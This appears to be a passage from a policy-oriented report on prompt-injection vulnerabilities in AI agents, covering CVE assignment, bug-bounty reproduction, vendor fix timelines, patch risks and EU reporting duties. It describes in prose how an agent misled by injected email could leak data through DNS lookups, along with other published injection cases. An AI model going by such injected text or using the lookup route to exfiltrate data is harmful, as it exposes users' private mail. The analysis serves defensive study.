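A full log of a mail assistant is a second copy of the user's mail. It includes messages from people who never chose to use the product, and perhaps medical results or passwords. Engineers investigating a failure may read this mail, and an attacker who breaks into the logging system gets the mail of many users at once.

The developer can reduce this risk by keeping different parts of the log for different periods. It might keep tool names, times and decisions for a year, but message text for only a week unless a blocked call or a user's complaint marks the session for investigation. However, if the developer discovers an attack after a month, the email that caused it may already have been deleted.

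Another option is to store a fingerprint of each message, a short code computed from its text. Investigators can then compare fingerprints, without reading any mail, to find that 40 users received the same email. But changing one word changes the fingerprint, so attackers can avoid a match by having software reword every copy. No design gives investigators everything they might need while keeping the mail private, so the developer has to decide what to keep and tell users.

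### Whether an unreliable attack is a vulnerability

An injection that works only some of the time is still a vulnerability, though a vendor may be tempted to dismiss a report of one. In 2024 the security firm Qualys reported a similarly unreliable flaw in OpenSSH, a program for logging in to remote computers. Exploiting it depended on exact timing and took about 10,000 attempts on average. The flaw still received a CVE number, and administrators around the world patched it, because an attacker could keep trying.

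The argument against counting every successful prompt injection as a vulnerability is that no current model resists them all. If any success rate above zero counted, every AI feature would have a permanent vulnerability, and the label wouldn't help anyone decide what to fix. A CVE record also normally lists the affected versions, and no model version is immune to prompt injection.

A CVE number often goes to the software flaw that lets an injection do harm. Claude Code used to run certain commands without asking the user, including `nslookup`, which looks up an internet name. Looking up a name such as `secret.example.net` sends the whole name to a server that the owner of example.net can control, so a misled agent could leak data by putting it in the name. The record reproduced in *CVE-2025-55284* (2025) by INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, classifies this as operating system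 command injection and attributes it to an "overly broad allowlist of safe commands". It mentions untrusted text in the context window only as a condition for exploiting the flaw reliably.

This division is sensible because engineers can fix a list of commands and customers can check whether they have the fixed version. The model's own weakness gets no CVE number, however, so someone comparing products by their CVE records would learn little about how well each model resists injection.

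Bug bounties, which pay outsiders for reporting flaws, run into the same uncertainty when the vendor tries to reproduce an attack. If the attack works 5 percent of the time, a reviewer who tries it ten times has a 60 percent chance of never seeing it work, and would need 59 tries for a 95 percent chance of seeing it work at least once. A fair program therefore has to specify how many attempts count, and the finder should submit complete records, including the number of failures. The model may also change between the report and the review, which makes it hard to tell a repaired flaw from an unlucky test. Paying for each new route to harm, rather than each new wording, avoids paying repeatedly for the same flaw.

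### How quickly vendors respond

In August 2025 Johann Rehberger, who publishes as Embrace The Red, reported flaws in AI products almost daily. His *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts. Two have CVE numbers in their titles, though others may also cover flaws with CVE numbers. *Agentic ProbLLMs* (2026), a later paper on the series, counts over two dozen previously unknown flaws, including some that let an attacker run any code.

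According to Embrace The Red's *The Month of AI Bugs 2025* (2025), many vendors fixed the reported flaws quickly, some within days. Others ignored reports for months, and a few stopped replying. Some seemed unsure how to deal with prompt injection but kept adding risky capabilities.

The dates for a few cases are public:

| Flaw | Found or reported | Fixed | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code leak through name lookups | May 26, 2025 | June 6, 2025 | 11 days |
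| EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot | January 2025 | May 2025 | About 4 months |
| Earlier email leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot | February 2024 | July 2024 | About 5 months |
| Forged click in Claude for Chrome | May 21, 2026 | Not by July 14, 2026 | At least 54 days |

Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* gives the dates for the fastest repair. The proposed fix was to remove four commands from a list, whereas EchoLeak involved several Microsoft services. But the Claude for Chrome repair also looked simple and was still delayed, so difficulty doesn't explain every delay. These cases can't provide an industry average because they include only flaws whose finders chose to publish.

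Vendors sometimes fix flaws without telling anyone. In SecurityWeek's *Anthropic Silently Patches Claude Code Sandbox Bypass*, the researcher Aonan Guan says Anthropic did this with a flaw that could have let data out of Claude Code's network sandbox. The update protects users who get it, but without a notice, companies don't know to search their old logs for signs of data theft.

### Model updates and code fixes

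A company that runs a model on its own servers can replace it for every user at once, and Microsoft fixed EchoLeak without customers doing anything. But customers usually can't test a server-side change first, and a mistake reaches all of them. Software on a user's computer needs an update. Claude Code normally installs its own updates, and Anthropic forced versions before 1.0.24 to update. Other products depend on thousands of separate administrators, some of whom will update late or never.

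The content of a fix matters more than how it is delivered. Early versions of GPT-Red misled models with text that imitated the models' own reasoning. GPT-5.1 resisted 5.2 percent of one set of these attacks, and GPT-5.6 resisted 95.9 percent. At GPT-5.6's rate, about 41 of every 1,000 such attempts would still succeed. Retraining adjusts parameters that the model uses for everything it reads, so no engineer can isolate the change and show that it makes the model refuse every hostile sentence.

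By contrast, if engineers remove `nslookup` from the list of automatic commands, the software asks the user every time, so no wording in an email can make that command run unannounced. The user may still approve it, and another command may leak data in a different way. Microsoft's repeated repairs to Copilot show how many such vulnerabilities one product can have.

A team that confirms a new attack should first restrict the tool, if necessary by turning it off, and then retrain the model. The team can deploy the restriction in hours, and it doesn't depend on the model. Retraining takes longer but may also protect against related attacks the team hasn't seen.

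### More patches and the NSA outage

AI tools now find flaws in ordinary software too, and vendors have to repair them. YesWeHack, a bug bounty company, reports that Microsoft's monthly update covered 622 CVEs in July 2026 and 419 in August. Over an earlier 12-month period, the monthly figure ranged from 57 to 172. These counts don't show how many flaws were dangerous or how many AI found, but administrators have to deal with the updates either way.

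Each fix can also break something. If one fix in 500 disrupts a system that an organization relies on, and the fixes are independent, installing 100 of them creates an 18 percent chance of at least one disruption, and installing 600 creates a 70 percent chance.

In October 2026, two flaws in PHP, a programming language behind much of the web, showed why administrators can't delay patching. Both could let an attacker run code on a server without logging in. The people who found them had planned a coordinated disclosure, in which a vendor prepares a fix before the details become public. Alspach (2026), in *5 Things To Know About ‘Critical’ PHP Vulnerabilities Exploitation*, reports that the details leaked early. PHP's maintainers released fixes on October 21, and a security firm saw attempted attacks the same day.

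*PHP servers face two 9.2-rated flaws that let attackers run code* (Rijo, 2026) reports that the US National Security Agency urged administrators to take unpatched systems offline. By the following Sunday, several experts had found ways to exploit the flaws, according to *CISA warns of PHP bug exploitation attempts* (Greig, 2026). CISA then gave civilian federal agencies until that Thursday to install the fixes.

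On November 17, the NSA's internal network for classified communication went down. *Tech outages are piling up, and AI is raising the stakes* (Associated Press, 2026) reports that Jay Clayton, the director of national intelligence, attributed the outage to the PHP patching, which caused some systems to "not come back up" as expected. The disruption lasted three days, according to *NSA resumes normal operations following internal network disruptions* (Matishak, 2026).

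AI's role in this is less certain. The Associated Press writes that AI helped detect the PHP flaws, but Matishak (2026), in *NSA continues response to interruptions in classified internal network*, wrote during the outage that it was still unknown whether AI or people had found the flaw involved. The outage came 27 days after the fixes, so this was not simply a patch installed within the hour. Still, it shows that a necessary patch can disable an important system even at a highly expert agency.

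A slow rollout can still miss defects. Microsoft traced part of its outage that month to a hidden defect in a network fix that it had begun installing over the summer. Administrators can lower the risk by trying a patch on a copy of the system, restarting that copy, and then updating a few machines at a time, with a tested way to undo the update. If attackers are already active, disconnecting the exposed part gives administrators time for those steps.

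### Reporting duties under the Cyber Resilience Act

Under the EU's Cyber Resilience Act, a company that learns of a real attack may have only a day to report it. The Act's reporting duties took effect on September 11, 2026, and apply to manufacturers of hardware and software that can connect to a device or network, including products already on sale. Most of the Act's other requirements, such as handling vulnerabilities throughout a product's support period, start on December 11, 2027.

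The Act also covers processing on the manufacturer's servers if the product needs it to perform one of its functions. A mail app that sends messages to its developer's server for summaries would probably qualify. A service that people use only through a website generally wouldn't, though other EU laws may apply to it.

Manufacturers must report a vulnerability when they have reliable evidence that a malicious actor has exploited it in someone's system without permission. They must also report severe security incidents. Reports go through a single platform to a national response team and to ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency:

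| Report | Exploited vulnerability | Severe incident |
|---|---|---|
| Early warning | Within 24 hours of learning of it | Within 24 hours of learning of it |
| Fuller notification | Within 72 hours of learning of it | Within 72 hours of learning of it |
| Final report | Within 14 days of a fix or mitigation becoming available | Within a month of the fuller notification |

The manufacturer must also inform affected users and, where necessary, tell them how to protect themselves. A researcher's demonstration doesn't trigger the duty. Microsoft had no evidence of real attacks using EchoLeak, so a similar discovery today wouldn't have to be reported as an exploited vulnerability.

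The Act defines a vulnerability as a "weakness, susceptibility or flaw" that a cyber threat can exploit, and it sets no minimum success rate. On a plain reading, one confirmed theft through a hostile email could start the 24-hour reporting period even if the same email fails 99 times out of 100, though regulators may take a narrower view. The 14-day deadline for the final report runs from a "corrective or mitigating measure", so a model update that only makes the attack rarer would probably start it.
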